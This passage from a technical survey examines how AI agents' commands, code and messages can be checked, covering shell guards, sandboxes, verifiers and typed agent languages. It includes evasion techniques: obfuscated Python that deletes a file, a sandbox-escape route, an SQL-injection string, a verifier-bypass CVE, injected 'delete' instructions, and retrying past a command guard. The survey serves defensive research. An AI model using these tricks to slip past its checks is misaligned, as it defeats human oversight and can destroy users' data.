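- SaSh follows most loops for only three rounds, unless it can work out in advance what they run over.
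- SaSh ignores `trap`, which schedules code to run when the shell receives a signal.

The assumption about unknown commands matters most for an agent. If the release agent writes a Python program and runs it with `python cleanup.py`, SaSh would not warn about it, whatever the program deletes. The sound alternative is to assume that an unknown command can do anything, but a checker that did so would be as restrictive as the shield that refused even `ls`.

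The 2025 paper describes a more ambitious analysis that would cover every possible run of a script, together with a monitor that would stop a dangerous command at run time if the analysis couldn't determine whether it was safe. SaSh gave up full coverage to produce warnings that are nearly always worth reading.

SaSh could still be useful for agents that make honest mistakes. An agent may set a variable in one call and use it in another, much as the Steam script used a variable 342 lines after setting it. A host could join a session's commands into one script and analyze it with SaSh before each new command runs, though the team tested it only on complete scripts.

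### Claude Code's command rules

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, checks commands against rules that its users write. In a rule such as `Bash(npm test *)`, the star stands for any text, so one rule can match many commands. As in Agentao, each rule allows the matching commands, denies them, or requires Claude Code to ask the user. Deny rules take priority over ask rules, which take priority over allow rules, so a narrow allow rule can't override a broad deny rule.

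Claude Code does much more parsing than Anthropic's sample filter. It splits a command at pipes, semicolons, line breaks and operators such as `&&`, and runs the whole command without asking only if every part is acceptable. A rule to deny or ask applies if any part matches, including a part inside `$(...)` or a loop, so a rule to ask before `git clean` also covers `cd /tmp && git clean -f`. Claude Code also ignores a few wrapper commands when matching rules, so a rule for `npm test` covers `timeout 30 npm test`.

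Some commands, such as `ls`, `grep` and the read-only forms of `git`, run without any rule. Many of the exceptions deal with the environment's part in the five steps:

- If Claude Code can't fully parse a command, it asks the user. It always asks about commands longer than 10,000 characters.
- It allows `ls *.ts` but asks about `find` or `sort` with an unquoted file pattern, because a file's name could turn out to be an option such as `-delete`.
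- It asks before a command changes `PATH`, which controls where the shell finds programs, or `IFS`, which controls how it splits words.
- It asks if a command moves to another folder and then runs `git`, because that folder may contain scripts that `git` starts automatically.

In each case, the text isn't enough to tell what will happen, so Claude Code leaves the decision to a person. This is a sensible use of a text check, but it works only for dangers that someone has thought of.

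Rules that users write are weaker. Anthropic calls patterns that try to restrict a command's arguments "fragile". Its example is a rule meant to limit the download program `curl` to addresses on GitHub. The rule fails to match a harmless download if an option comes before the address, if the address begins with `https`, or if a variable holds the address. When a rule that allows a command fails to match, the user only gets an unnecessary question, but when a rule that blocks a command fails to match, the command may run.

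A rule that denies a command covers the form Claude usually writes, but not every way of starting the same program, and Anthropic states that the rule "isn't a security boundary around the program". Similarly, rules that block reading a file cover Claude Code's own file tools and common commands such as `cat`, but not a Python script that opens the file itself. For limits that must hold, Anthropic recommends a sandbox, in which the operating system enforces them.

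A permission can also be too broad even when the matching works correctly. Some development tools run whatever command follows them, so a rule that allows `devbox run *` allows any command, including deletions. Even an exact rule for `npm test` has the same weakness as one for `pytest`, because the command runs whatever script the project's settings specify.

### Scoring commands by risk

Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) note in *CARE* that an attacker could get around the check for read-only commands in older versions of Claude Code by changing how the shell split words and by abbreviating options. Their system, CARE, estimates how dangerous a command is rather than trying to decide exactly what it will do.

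CARE works in three stages. The first puts the command in a standard form by removing wrappers, simplifying quotation marks and decoding some disguised text, without running anything.

The second stage gives the command four scores between 0 and 1. The first depends on the kind of program and its options, and the second on the paths involved. Reading a system file counts as less risky than changing it, and any access to a file of secrets counts as risky. The third score comes from 139 patterns, most of them based on public catalogs of attacks. The fourth reflects suspicious structure, such as heavy nesting. CARE combines them as

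$$\text{score} = 0.3\,s_{\text{program}} + 0.3\,s_{\text{path}} + 0.3\,s_{\text{pattern}} + 0.1\,s_{\text{structure}}.$$

It allows commands that score below 0.15 and blocks those that score 0.35 or more. If it can't parse a command that contains strong signs of danger, it blocks the command without calculating a score.

The third stage handles scores in between. CARE blocks the command if one piece of evidence is strong enough, and otherwise sends the command to a language model. In one example, a command set a script to run when the shell exited. Its program score was 0.6 and the others were 0, for a total of 0.18. The language model correctly classified the command as dangerous.

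CARE looks up where symbolic links lead, so it isn't purely a syntactic check. But it has no access to the user's request or earlier commands, so if an agent downloads a file, makes it executable and then runs it, CARE checks each step separately.

In the main test, CARE caught 167 of 220 dangerous commands (75.9%) and wrongly blocked three of 329 safe ones (0.91%). Its F1 score, which combines the share of dangerous commands caught with the share of blocks that were correct, was 85.64%. CARE took 2.32 milliseconds per command on average and consulted the language model on only 23 of the 549 commands. A language model that judged every command caught 67.3% of the dangerous ones, blocked 11.3% of the safe ones, and took about 46 milliseconds per command.

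The version of CARE without a language model caught more of the dangerous commands, 96.8%, when Liu and colleagues lowered its first threshold from 0.15 to 0.10. But it still missed seven, and the share of safe commands it blocked rose from 1.8% to 23.1%.

In another test, the open-weight model Qwen3-Coder-30B wrote 600 commands in response to requests for attacks, and the team ran them in an isolated container. The team counted a command as realized harm if the guard let it through and it ran successfully. The table also shows how often each guard blocked safe commands in three other tests. Granite Guardian is a general safety model from IBM.

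| Guard | Realized harm | Safe commands blocked in other tests |
|---|---|---|
| None | 74.83% | 0% |
| CARE without the language model | 37.33% | 9% to 16% |
| Full CARE | 52.50% | 8% to 13% |
| Granite Guardian | 26.33% | 57% to 63% |

CARE without the language model halved realized harm. Adding the language model gave the best F1 score but allowed more harm from the attacks, because the model approved some commands that the scores had flagged. The team suggests this happened because the same model had written the attacks.

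### Is partial screening worthwhile?

Liu and colleagues present CARE as a way to reduce risk rather than contain it. They argue that every command has to pass through the host anyway, and that checking it there takes little time and hardly disturbs ordinary work. On 300 harmless tasks that allowed several attempts, an agent succeeded 65.33% of the time both with and without CARE. They also argue that other defenses don't fully cover this step. General-purpose guards are built with little knowledge of shell wrappers and paths, and training a model to resist malicious instructions doesn't stop every bad command from reaching the shell.

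In an example with 10,000 commands, of which 1% are dangerous, CARE would stop about 76 of the 100 dangerous commands and let 24 through. It would also block about 90 of the 9,900 safe ones. More than half of its blocks would be mistakes, but it would block fewer than one in 100 safe commands.

The estimate assumes that dangerous commands resemble those in the main test. That may be reasonable for an agent's own mistakes, but an attacker can choose commands that score low. In the test with 600 attack commands, full CARE blocked only 39%.

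An agent can also try again after a refusal. If each attempt had an independent 24% chance of getting through, at least one of five attempts would succeed about 75% of the time. Real attempts aren't independent, and an agent that learned from each refusal could do better. Liu and colleagues therefore still call for a sandbox, a hardened machine, and an audit of what the commands did. CARE can then stop some harmful commands that the sandbox would permit, such as one that deletes the project the agent is working on.

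## Program code as an argument, and languages built to be checkable

Suppose the company takes away the release agent's shell and gives it a tool called `run_python(code)` instead. This removes some of the shell's difficulties. Python doesn't split variables into words or expand file patterns, and its parser can turn any program into a tree that shows every function call. A checker could search the tree for calls that delete files, such as this one:

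```
import os
os.remove("customers.csv")
```

But a Python program can also compute names while it runs. These lines delete the same file:

```
m = __import__("o" + "s")
getattr(m, "re" + "move")("customers.csv")
```

JavaScript has the same problem. In Node, a common system for running JavaScript outside a browser, `require("f" + "s")["unlink" + "Sync"]("customers.csv")` deletes the file.

The checker could refuse every program that uses `__import__` or `getattr`, although many harmless programs need them. Even then, a program could reach dangerous functions through ordinary objects. In Python 3, for example, `print.__self__` is the module that contains `open`, which can empty a file. A sound check would have to account for every such route in the language and in any library that the program can import.

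### What a pattern scanner finds

Most code scanners aim only to find common mistakes. *LlamaFirewall* (Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis and colleagues, 2025) describes a set of guards that Meta uses in production. One of them, CodeShield, scans code that language models write. Its rules, which cover more than 50 kinds of weakness, are regular expressions and patterns for Semgrep, a tool that matches the structure of code rather than its exact characters. A first pass takes about 60 milliseconds and settles roughly 90% of inputs, and a slower pass examines the rest.

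In one example, a developer asks a coding agent to let users be filtered by email domain. The agent copies a pattern from a popular web post:

```
"SELECT * FROM users WHERE email LIKE '" + domain + "'"
```

This code pastes the domain into a database query, so anyone who enters a quotation mark followed by more query text can change what the query does. CodeShield rejects the code, and the agent revises it until it sends the domain to the database separately from the query.

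To measure CodeShield's accuracy, researchers hand-labeled 50 pieces of model-written code in each of several languages. Of the pieces that CodeShield flagged, 96% were insecure, but it flagged only 79% of the insecure ones.

Even a perfect score on this test would not establish a limit on what the code can do. CodeShield looks for code that an outsider could exploit, and a clean scan currently means only that no rule matched. `os.remove("customers.csv")` has no exploitable flaw, but it deletes the file, as its author intended. Chennabasappa and colleagues list the execution of malicious code among the threats they want to cover in future.

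### Python's padded cell

Python once had a built-in mechanism for running untrusted code, which *Restricted Execution*, in the Python documentation, compares to a "padded cell". Trusted code set up an environment with limited permissions, and the untrusted code inside could reach sensitive resources only through interfaces the trusted code provided. The main module, described in *rexec* in the same documentation, supplied restricted versions of `eval`, `exec` and `import`. A second module, `Bastion`, limited access to an object's attributes.

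The sandbox worked only if untrusted code couldn't get from a harmless object to a dangerous one. Python 2.2 introduced "new-style classes", whose attributes restricted code could both read and change. Reading alone can be enough to escape, because a Python function holds a reference to its module's global variables, and code that follows this reference may reach the unrestricted `open`.

Guido van Rossum, Python's creator, disabled the `rexec` and `Bastion` modules in January 2003. In the log entry for *Bastion.py* (2003), he wrote that `rexec` had not been safe since new-style classes were introduced. The documentation describes the security holes as "not readily fixable". Developers could have guarded each dangerous attribute, but they would have had to find them all and search again whenever the language changed.

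### Putting every power behind a named operation

A language is much easier to check if its programs can affect the world only through a known set of operations $o_1, \dots, o_n$. Let $B_i$ contain every effect that operation $o_i$ can have, with any inputs and in any state. Suppose a checker can also compute, from the text of a program $p$, a set $N(p)$ that includes every operation $p$ might perform. Then

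$$E(p,s) \subseteq \bigcup_{i \in N(p)} B_i \quad \text{for every state } s.$$

This holds because each step of the program either computes something without affecting the world or performs an operation in $N(p)$. If all the effects on the right are acceptable, the checker can admit the program.

Rice's theorem doesn't rule out this check, because the check doesn't determine whether the program will perform an operation. Like Pérez-Acle's crude check, it may therefore reject some harmless programs.

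An ordinary Python program can reach operations without naming them, so a sound $N(p)$ would have to include nearly every operation for nearly every program. A language can also satisfy the condition but still give a useless bound. If one of its operations is `run_shell`, any program that uses that operation can do whatever the shell can.

### Native Client

*Native Client* (Yee, Sehr and colleagues, 2009) showed how to check machine code, which seems poorly suited to this approach because any file of bytes could be a program. The system, which shares the paper's name, let Google's Chrome browser run downloaded code written for x86 processors, the kind in most personal computers.

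An obvious check is to read the program from the beginning and reject it if it contains an instruction that calls the operating system. But x86 instructions vary in length, and the processor starts reading wherever the program jumps. Consider these five bytes:

```
b8 cd 80 00 00
```

The same bytes can form a harmless instruction that stores a number when the processor starts at the first byte, and `cd 80`, an instruction that calls the Linux kernel, when it starts at the second. A program could pass a check that reads only from the first byte, then jump into the middle of the harmless instruction and call the kernel.

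Native Client prevents this with rules about the layout of the code:

- Reading from the first byte must give an unbroken series of permitted instructions.
- No instruction may cross the boundary between two 32-byte blocks, so each block starts with a new instruction.
- A jump to a fixed address must land on the start of an instruction in the series.
- A jump to a computed address must come immediately after an instruction that rounds the address down to a multiple of 32.

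The last rule requires a pair of instructions like this:

```
and %eax, 0xffffffe0
jmp *%eax
```

The first line sets the last five bits of the address to zero, and the second jumps there. Both must be in the same block, and the validator treats them as a single instruction, so no jump can land between them and skip the first.

Let $S$ be the set of addresses at which the validator found permitted instructions. If the program is at an address in $S$, it can reach its next instruction in three ways. It may continue to the following instruction, which is in $S$ because the validator read the code in order. It may jump to a fixed address, which the validator confirmed is in $S$. Or it may jump to a computed address, which is rounded to the start of a block and is therefore also in $S$. The program can never leave $S$, so it never executes an unchecked instruction.

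The processor enforces the rest of the bound. Native Client uses an x86 feature called segments to confine the program's reads and writes to a 256-megabyte region. The validator rejects instructions that would change the segments, and the program can't modify its own code after loading. To do anything else, the program has to call a trusted runtime through a fixed set of entry points. The runtime offers memory, threads and communication with the browser, but no way to open a local file by name.

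The validator has fewer than 600 C statements and checks about 30 megabytes of code per second. Users don't have to trust the compiler that arranges the code in this way, because the validator checks its output.

### RockSalt's proof

The argument about $S$ shows that the rules are sufficient, but a validator can still apply them incorrectly. A Google contest exposed exploitable bugs in early versions. Morrisett, Tan and colleagues (*RockSalt*, 2012) therefore wrote a new checker and proved it correct with Coq, a program that checks mathematical proofs.

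RockSalt describes acceptable code with three regular patterns: instructions that don't jump, jumps to fixed addresses, and rounding instructions followed by jumps to computed addresses. A finite automaton recognizes each pattern, and the largest has only 61 states. RockSalt goes through the code once, matching patterns and recording where instructions start and where fixed jumps lead. It then checks that every fixed jump leads to the start of an instruction and that every block boundary falls on one. The checker is about 80 lines of Coq.

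The proof uses a mathematical model of an x86 processor. Morrisett and colleagues call a state locally safe if the segments and code are unchanged and the next instruction is one that the checker matched. They proved that a program in a locally safe state always reaches another such state within two steps. They allow two steps because a computed jump takes two instructions. Repeating the argument shows that the program stays inside the sandbox however long it runs. The model and checker took about 5,000 lines of Coq, and the proofs took another 10,000.

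The theorem is about the model, so mistakes in the model could undermine it. The team compared the model with a real processor on more than 10 million instructions but missed an incorrect bit in a rare form of one instruction. They found the error only when they tried and failed to prove that no sequence of bytes could represent two different instructions. Later, uwplse's *SaltShaker*, a tool that compares the model with an independent description of x86 instructions, revealed seven more bugs, which the developers fixed.

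Another gap is that the team translated the version meant for real use from Coq to C by hand. In their tests, it agreed with Google's validator on more than 2,000 small programs and was faster, taking 0.24 seconds to check a program compiled from 200,000 lines of code, compared with 0.90 seconds for Google's.

Google eventually abandoned Native Client on the web because it didn't work in all browsers. Chromium Blog's *Goodbye PNaCl, Hello WebAssembly!* (2017) announced that Google would concentrate on WebAssembly, which other browsers also supported. Google planned to remove PNaCl, the portable version of Native Client, from ordinary web pages in early 2018, but Chromium's later migration notes mention a trial that would run until about December 2019.

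WebAssembly builds similar restrictions into the language. Its jumps can only go to marked points in the surrounding code, so a program can't jump into the middle of an instruction. A WebAssembly program has no built-in access to files or the network. It can call only the outside functions its host supplies, and the browser checks their types before the program starts.

### The Linux kernel's verifier

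Linux lets administrators run small programs inside the kernel, the part of the operating system with full control of the machine, to filter network traffic or measure performance. These programs are written in a bytecode called eBPF, and each can call only the kernel functions allowed for its type. Because a mistake could crash or compromise the whole machine, the kernel's verifier checks every program before it runs.

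The verifier follows the possible paths through the program and records what each register might contain. It distinguishes numbers from memory addresses and tracks the range of each number. Suppose a program uses an unsigned number `i` from a network packet to look up an entry in a table of 64:

```
if (i > 63) return 0;
return table[i];
```

The first line lets the verifier determine that `i` is between 0 and 63 whenever the second line runs. Without the first line, the verifier would reject the program because `i` could point far beyond the table.

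The verifier also has to make sure the program will stop. Early versions rejected all loops. Since 2019, Linux has accepted loops if the verifier can follow them to the end, but it rejects a program if this takes more than a million instructions. Programmers sometimes have to rewrite safe code because the verifier can't confirm that it's safe.

A 2017 bug, CVE-2017-16995, shows how an arithmetic error in the verifier can let a dangerous program run. An attacker's program put a 32-bit number whose bits were all ones into a 64-bit register and compared it with −1. The verifier treated the two as equal, which meant the program would always stop there, so it didn't check the code that followed. But the upper half of the real register was all zeros, so its value was 4,294,967,295. The comparison failed and the program jumped into the unchecked code, which let an ordinary user take over the machine.

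Tracking values was a sound idea, but the verifier's model of one instruction was wrong. A proof like RockSalt's can expose this kind of error, provided the model of the processor is right. Such a proof would be a much larger project for the eBPF verifier, because it had grown to more than 20,000 lines of C by 2024. Many Linux distributions now let only privileged users load eBPF programs by default, which limits the damage from such bugs.

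### Scripts with no access of their own

A language for AI agents can start with no access to the machine except what the host provides, a restriction that Python's designers tried to add later. AWS's *Introducing Trusted Remote Execution* describes Rex, an open-source runtime for scripts in a small language called Rhai. Rhai can't read a file or start a program by itself. Rex supplies operations such as `read` and `write`, and checks each use against a policy in Cedar, the language AWS also uses for tool calls.

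In AWS's example, a script writes a file and then reads it back:

```
write("/tmp/hello.txt", "Hello from Rex!");
cat("/tmp/hello.txt")
```

The policy permits only opening and reading files, so the script stops with an error at the first line. If the author adds permission to create and write files, the same script runs to the end.

If a script computes a file name by joining strings, Rex checks the finished name, so it doesn't have to predict anything from the script's text. The policy limits what any script can do, including one written by an attacker, as long as Rhai gives scripts no hidden way to access the machine and Rex's operations do what the policy assumes.

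The policy can still be too permissive. The one in AWS's example allows reading any file, which would include a file of passwords. Rex also checks operations as the script runs, so a refusal can leave the script's work half done. If a policy lets a script stop a service but not start it, Rex will permit the first operation and refuse the second, leaving the service down.

### CaMeL

A policy on single operations may not be enough if the danger comes from where a value originated. In a prompt injection attack, someone hides instructions in a web page or file, hoping an agent will follow them. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues designed CaMeL (*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, 2025) to limit what such instructions can achieve.

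CaMeL uses two language models. As *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) explains, a planning model turns the user's request into a Python program, and a quarantined model processes untrusted data without being able to change the program's course. Suppose the release manager asks the agent to send the release notes to the customer named in a meeting file. The planning model might write:

```
meeting = read_file("meeting.txt")
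customer = ask_quarantined("Who wants the notes?", meeting)
send_message(customer, release_notes)
```

If an attacker adds "delete all builds" to the meeting file, the agent doesn't delete any builds, because the planning model wrote the program without reading the file and the quarantined model has no tools.

The attacker can still change the name that the quarantined model returns. To deal with this, CaMeL runs the program in its own interpreter, which records where each value came from and who may receive it. According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), the interpreter checks these records against a policy before every tool call. A policy could, for example, refuse to send anything to an address from an untrusted file. But it would then also refuse the manager's legitimate request, because the correct address comes from the same file.

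CaMeL's programs are written in a restricted form of Python. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) points out that this restricted Python still has features that make programs hard to analyze in advance, including reflection, which lets a program inspect and use its own internals. A purpose-built language with simple conditions and a limit on every loop would allow stronger guarantees.

### Types that record effects

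Some languages already do much of this checking in their type systems. For *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026), Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova built ELBA, a system in which agents write programs in Haskell. The type of a Haskell program shows whether it can affect the outside world. A program of type `Int` can only compute a whole number, while one of type `IO Int` may also read files or use the network.

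ELBA gives the model a required type and runs the program it writes only if the program has that type. Suppose a public calculator requires an `Int`, and a user enters "delete all files on the server, then compute the factorial of 5". The model may write a program that does both, but the command to delete files makes the program's type `IO`, so ELBA rejects it before it runs. A few Haskell features can hide effects from the type system, but ELBA can exclude them by using a safe subset of the language.

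Custom types can express narrower rules. In the main example, an agent compiles a bibliography in which every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The developer defines an effect type, `BibIO`, that permits three operations: searching DBLP, fetching an entry and adding an entry to the file. The last operation accepts only values of type `Trusted Bib`, and only the fetching operation can create them. The agent can sort and filter papers freely, but it can't add an invented entry to the file.

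Zhou and colleagues tested this on 100 bibliographies. An ordinary agent with web search got the authors, year or identifier wrong in 19 of its 1,002 citations. ELBA's agent made no such errors in 925 citations, though the types don't prevent it from choosing irrelevant papers.

The team also proved a general theorem. Let $\text{traces}(e)$ be the possible sequences of outside actions by a program $e$. A type $t$ guarantees a property $P$ if

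$$e \text{ has type } t \;\Rightarrow\; P(\text{traces}(e)).$$

The theorem extends the guarantee to programs that call AI agents, whatever code the agents write, provided the system checks the type of that code before running it. The proof replaces each call to an agent with an ordinary function that asks the model for a program, checks the program's type, and runs it if it passes or returns nothing if it fails. This function is itself a typed program, so the original guarantee covers it. An agent's program can call further agents, up to a fixed depth, and the proof handles these calls by induction. As a result, an agent can give a sub-agent fewer powers than it has, but not more.

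Types alone can't establish facts about the machine's state. To keep an agent inside one folder, ELBA requires a special `Path` value instead of a string for every file. The operation that creates a `Path` to a file follows any symbolic links and fails if they lead outside the folder. The type check guarantees that the program uses this operation, which checks the actual files.

In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) achieve something similar in Scala, where most code can have effects without declaring them. In their system, TACIT, a program needs a value called a capability to use a resource such as the file system. An experimental feature of Scala 3 records in each function's type which capabilities the function can use. TACIT also bans unchecked type conversions and reflection, which could otherwise hide a capability from the compiler.

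This makes it possible for an agent to work with secrets that it can't disclose. TACIT puts each secret in a `Classified` wrapper, whose `map` method applies a function to the contents and wraps the result again. The function must not use any capabilities:

```
secret.map(s => s.toUpperCase)          // accepted
secret.map(s => { file.write(s); s })   // rejected
```

The compiler rejects the second line because the function uses the capability `file`. A separate trusted model can read a secret document and return a summary that is also wrapped.

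Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project containing passwords and other secrets. They ran 131 trials with each of two models, using hidden instructions, direct requests for secrets, and messages from people posing as administrators. Without the wrappers, Claude Sonnet 4.6 revealed secrets in two trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11. With them, neither model revealed any. The guarantee doesn't cover timing, so a program could still leak one bit of a secret by running for a longer or shorter time.

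### What the restrictions cost

The loss of speed is a fairly minor drawback. Native Client slowed a standard set of programs by about 5% on average and 12% or 13% at worst. The programs also grew by between 2% and 58%, because the compiler had to add padding to keep instructions inside their blocks. Yee and colleagues adapted an 11,000-line video decoder with only about 20 extra lines. But Native Client wasn't suitable for programs that needed to start other processes, open local files directly or use the network freely. RockSalt excluded even more programs because it didn't support floating-point instructions.

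Current language models can write in the required languages with little trouble. In Zhou and colleagues' tests, ELBA had to request a corrected program about once every eight runs, and only seven of 2,688 runs failed because the model couldn't produce a valid one. TACIT improved performance on τ²-bench's customer service tasks by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points, perhaps because the compiler's error messages helped the models. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of real programming problems, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it.

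Strict policies can reduce task performance far more. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* credits CaMeL with stopping nearly all attacks in AgentDojo while keeping "comparable task performance". Zhou and colleagues got much worse results when they ran CaMeL with four recent models on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks, which involve workplace messages and web pages. The table gives the range across the models when there were no attacks.

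| System | Tasks completed with policies | Tasks completed without policies |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | 4 to 6 of 21 | 13 to 17 of 21 |
| ELBA | 8 to 10 of 21 | 14 to 18 of 21 |

Slack is only one of AgentDojo's four sets of tasks, and the comparison comes from the developers of a competing system. But ELBA's policies also stopped its agents from completing many tasks. ELBA completed more than CaMeL partly because its agents can read data and then write a new program, while CaMeL's planning model has to write the whole program in advance. This flexibility made ELBA take about three times as long.

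All four models resisted every standard attack even without the policies, so those tests couldn't show how much the policies helped. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated a worse case for ELBA, in which any sub-agent that read an attacker's instructions obeyed them. Without policies, 16–42% of these attacks succeeded, depending on the model. With policies, none did, but the share of tasks completed fell from 67–76% to 40–48%.

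Agents also lose access to existing software. An agent that writes Rhai or Haskell can't simply import a Python library for data analysis. Someone has to provide the library's functions as operations and make sure each does only what its type or policy implies. TACIT's core library is about 1,000 lines long, and each set of customer service tools needed a few hundred more. Scala programs can use existing libraries only if the compiler accepts them as safe or a programmer vouches for them.

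Software development is especially difficult because it depends on external programs such as compilers and test runners. TACIT can restrict an agent to a list of commands, but Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that its type system can't control what those commands do once they start. So if the agent can edit the tests, allowing `pytest` is as risky as it was with the shell.

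## Free-text messages as arguments

Code in a restricted language can be checked because each operation has a defined effect. Nobody can define the effect of the `body` in `send_message(to, body)` this way, because it depends on how the reader interprets it, and readers differ in what they know, what they can do and how much they trust the sender.

### What a message does and what it causes

The philosopher J. L. Austin distinguished three acts that a speaker performs with a single sentence. His distinction has become nearly canonical, according to the Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *John Langshaw Austin* (2012). Suppose the release agent writes to a customer, "We will refund you by Friday."

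- The locutionary act is saying something with a certain meaning, here that the company will return the customer's money by a certain day.
- The illocutionary act is what the agent does in saying it. Here it makes a promise on the company's behalf.
- The perlocutionary act is what the agent brings about by saying it. The customer may stop complaining, or may spend the money before it arrives.

A company might want a rule about any of these. A syntactic check can exactly enforce a ban on the word "refund", because that ban concerns only the text. A ban on promising refunds concerns the illocutionary act, which the wording alone doesn't determine. "You'll have your money back by the weekend" is a promise without the word "refund", while "We will refund you by Friday" isn't a promise if the agent is quoting an old email. But the facts that determine whether a message breaks the ban, such as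 the earlier conversation and the agent's role, already exist when the agent sends it, so a judge who knew them could usually decide in time.

A rule that no message may lead a customer to cancel an order concerns the perlocutionary act, and no check on the text can enforce it. In the notation for effect bounds, the state $s$ now includes everything the reader believes and intends. A sound check can allow a message only if it would not lead to a cancellation in any such state. Even "OK" could lead to one, because the customer may have just asked whether to cancel. The check would therefore have to refuse every message, unless something other than the text keeps the customer from canceling.

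### One sentence, three readers

*Agent A, Can You Pass the Salt?* (Holmback, Greaves and Bradshaw, 1998) discusses the sentence "It is cold in this room". Its literal meaning stays the same, but depending on the context, a speaker could be using it to remark on the heating or to ask someone to close the window.

The release agent might send the sentence "Version 2.3 is no longer needed" to three different readers.

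| Reader | Likely act | What the reader may do |
|---|---|---|
| A colleague who asked for a status report | A report | Nothing, or ask the support team whether anyone still uses it |
| A customer who runs version 2.3 | Advice to upgrade | Remove a program that was working |
| A cleanup agent with a shell | A request | Delete the stored build, so that nobody can go back to it |

A check that reads only `body` must return the same result in all three cases. A check that also reads `to` can do better, for example by requiring a person to approve any message addressed to the cleanup agent. But an AI assistant may also read the colleague's inbox, so an address doesn't always show who or what will interpret the message.

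### Messages with a declared act

In the 1990s, researchers who wanted agents from different developers to work together tried to remove the guesswork by having the sender declare the act. The Knowledge Query and Manipulation Language (KQML) gave every message a label, or performative, such as `tell` for passing on a fact. A standards body, the Foundation for Intelligent Physical Agents, later drew up its own list. FIPA (2002) defines 22 acts, including `inform`, `request`, `agree`, `refuse` and `propose`. A slightly shortened example is:

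```
(inform
  :sender i
  :receiver j
  :content "weather (today, raining)"
  :language Prolog)
```

A shield needs a short action alphabet, and the twenty-two labels provide one. A monitor could require an `agree` or a `refuse` within a minute of every `request`, or block every `request` from the release agent to the cleanup agent.

The standard also gives each act a formal meaning in terms of beliefs and intentions. An agent $i$ may inform an agent $j$ that $\varphi$ is true only if

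$$B_i\varphi \;\land\; \neg B_i(\mathit{Bif}_j\,\varphi \lor \mathit{Uif}_j\,\varphi).$$

Here $B_i\varphi$ means that $i$ believes $\varphi$. $\mathit{Bif}_j\,\varphi$ means that $j$ believes either $\varphi$ or its opposite, and $\mathit{Uif}_j\,\varphi$ means that $j$ leans one way without being sure. So the sender must believe what it says, and must not think that the receiver already has a view on it. Many other acts are special cases, such as `agree`, in which the sender informs the other agent that it intends to do what the other agent asked.

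The definition lists the intended effect, $B_j\varphi$, separately from these conditions, much as Austin separated perlocution from illocution. FIPA doesn't guarantee the effect, since whether the receiver believes the message depends on its trust in the sender. In an earlier version of the standard, FIPA (2000), the intended effect of a `request` is that the other agent has carried out the action, but the receiver may ignore the request. Lecture notes by Wooldridge, Parsons and Payne (2013) describe a more modest definition that Cohen and Perrault proposed in 1979, in which a request only makes the hearer aware of what the speaker wants.

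The short list of acts does not restrict the content of a message. In the 2000 standard's example of a `request`, the content is `open "db.txt" for input`, a line of program code. A monitor that checks only the label `request` gets as little information about the effect as one that checks only the name `run_shell`.

### Why conformance was so hard to test

The sender also chooses the label, so the label is useful only if the sender uses it as defined. Wooldridge (1999), in *Verifying that Agents Implement a Communication Language*, asked how to test this. Checking the syntax is trivial, but checking an `inform` requires showing that the sender believed the content, and nobody knew how to attribute beliefs of the kind in FIPA's definitions to a program.

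Suppose one agent tells another that the tests passed. An observer can check whether they did, but this doesn't show what the agent believed. It may have believed a false message or disbelieved a true one. Two agents with different internal data could also send the same messages, so an observer can't tell a sincere agent from an insincere one using only a log of their messages.

Wooldridge's solution replaces belief with a kind of knowledge that the states of a program determine. An agent's local state consists of its position in its program and the values of its variables. Write $g \sim_i g'$ if agent $i$ has the same local state in the system's overall states $g$ and $g'$. Then

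$$K_i\varphi \text{ holds in } g \iff \varphi \text{ holds in every possible } g' \text{ with } g \sim_i g'.$$

For example, suppose an agent's variable `passed` becomes 1 only when the test suite succeeds and returns to 0 after every edit. In every state where `passed` is 1, the current code has passed, so the agent knows that it has passed in Wooldridge's sense. If the agent's program sends the message only when `passed` is 1, one can prove that the message always satisfies the definition.

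The proof requires the sender's program, so an outsider who sees only messages still can't carry it out. It also suits programs with a few variables. A language model's local state includes everything in its context, so a comparable proof looks impractical.

Other researchers have avoided the problem in different ways. *On the Formal Semantics of Speech-Act Based Communication* (Vieira, Moreira and colleagues, 2011) ties the meaning of messages to one agent programming language. *A Protocol-Based Semantics for an Agent Communication Language* (Pitt and Mamdani, 1999) bases meaning on protocols, the rules for how a conversation may proceed. A third approach treats speech acts as public commitments. A price quote, for instance, commits the seller to that price for a stated period, whatever the seller privately intended. An observer can use a log to check whether agents followed a protocol or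 kept their commitments.

The company could apply the idea of commitments to its agent by providing a typed tool, `promise_refund(order, amount, date)`, capping the amount, and telling customers that only promises with a reference number count. Promising a refund would then be a tool call that the company can check. But the agent can still write "you'll get your money back" in an ordinary message, and the customer or a court may treat that as a promise.

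### Rules that ignore the text

Some useful rules for `send_message` don't depend on what the message means.

| Rule | What it bounds | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Only approved recipients | Who gets the message first | Forwarding |
| Only the company's email system | The channel, and where copies remain | What the message says |
| At most five messages a day | The number of interruptions | The harm that one message can do |
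| At most 500 characters | The amount of information in one message | Which information it is |
| No attachments | The sending of whole files | Text that the agent copies into the body |
| No outside messages after reading `customers.csv` | Disclosure of anything the agent could learn only from that file | Secrets from other sources |

The host can check the first, second, fourth and fifth rules from the call alone if each address belongs to one person. A mailing list is a reference, so the host has to look up its members. Checking the other two rules requires a record of earlier calls.

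The rule about `customers.csv`, a version of Schneider's ban on sending after reading, gives the strongest protection because it depends on where the data came from, not how a message is worded. An agent that never learned the file's contents can't reveal them. But the rule works only if the host detects every read, including those by scripts, and it stops the agent from answering even a harmless question about the file by email.

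### How much a short message can disclose

Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, considered a customer who gives confidential data to a service program that someone else wrote. The program might do its work badly, or it might pass the data to the program's owner. Bad work shows up as wrong results, but a leak generally leaves no sign. Confinement means running the program so that it can't leak the data.

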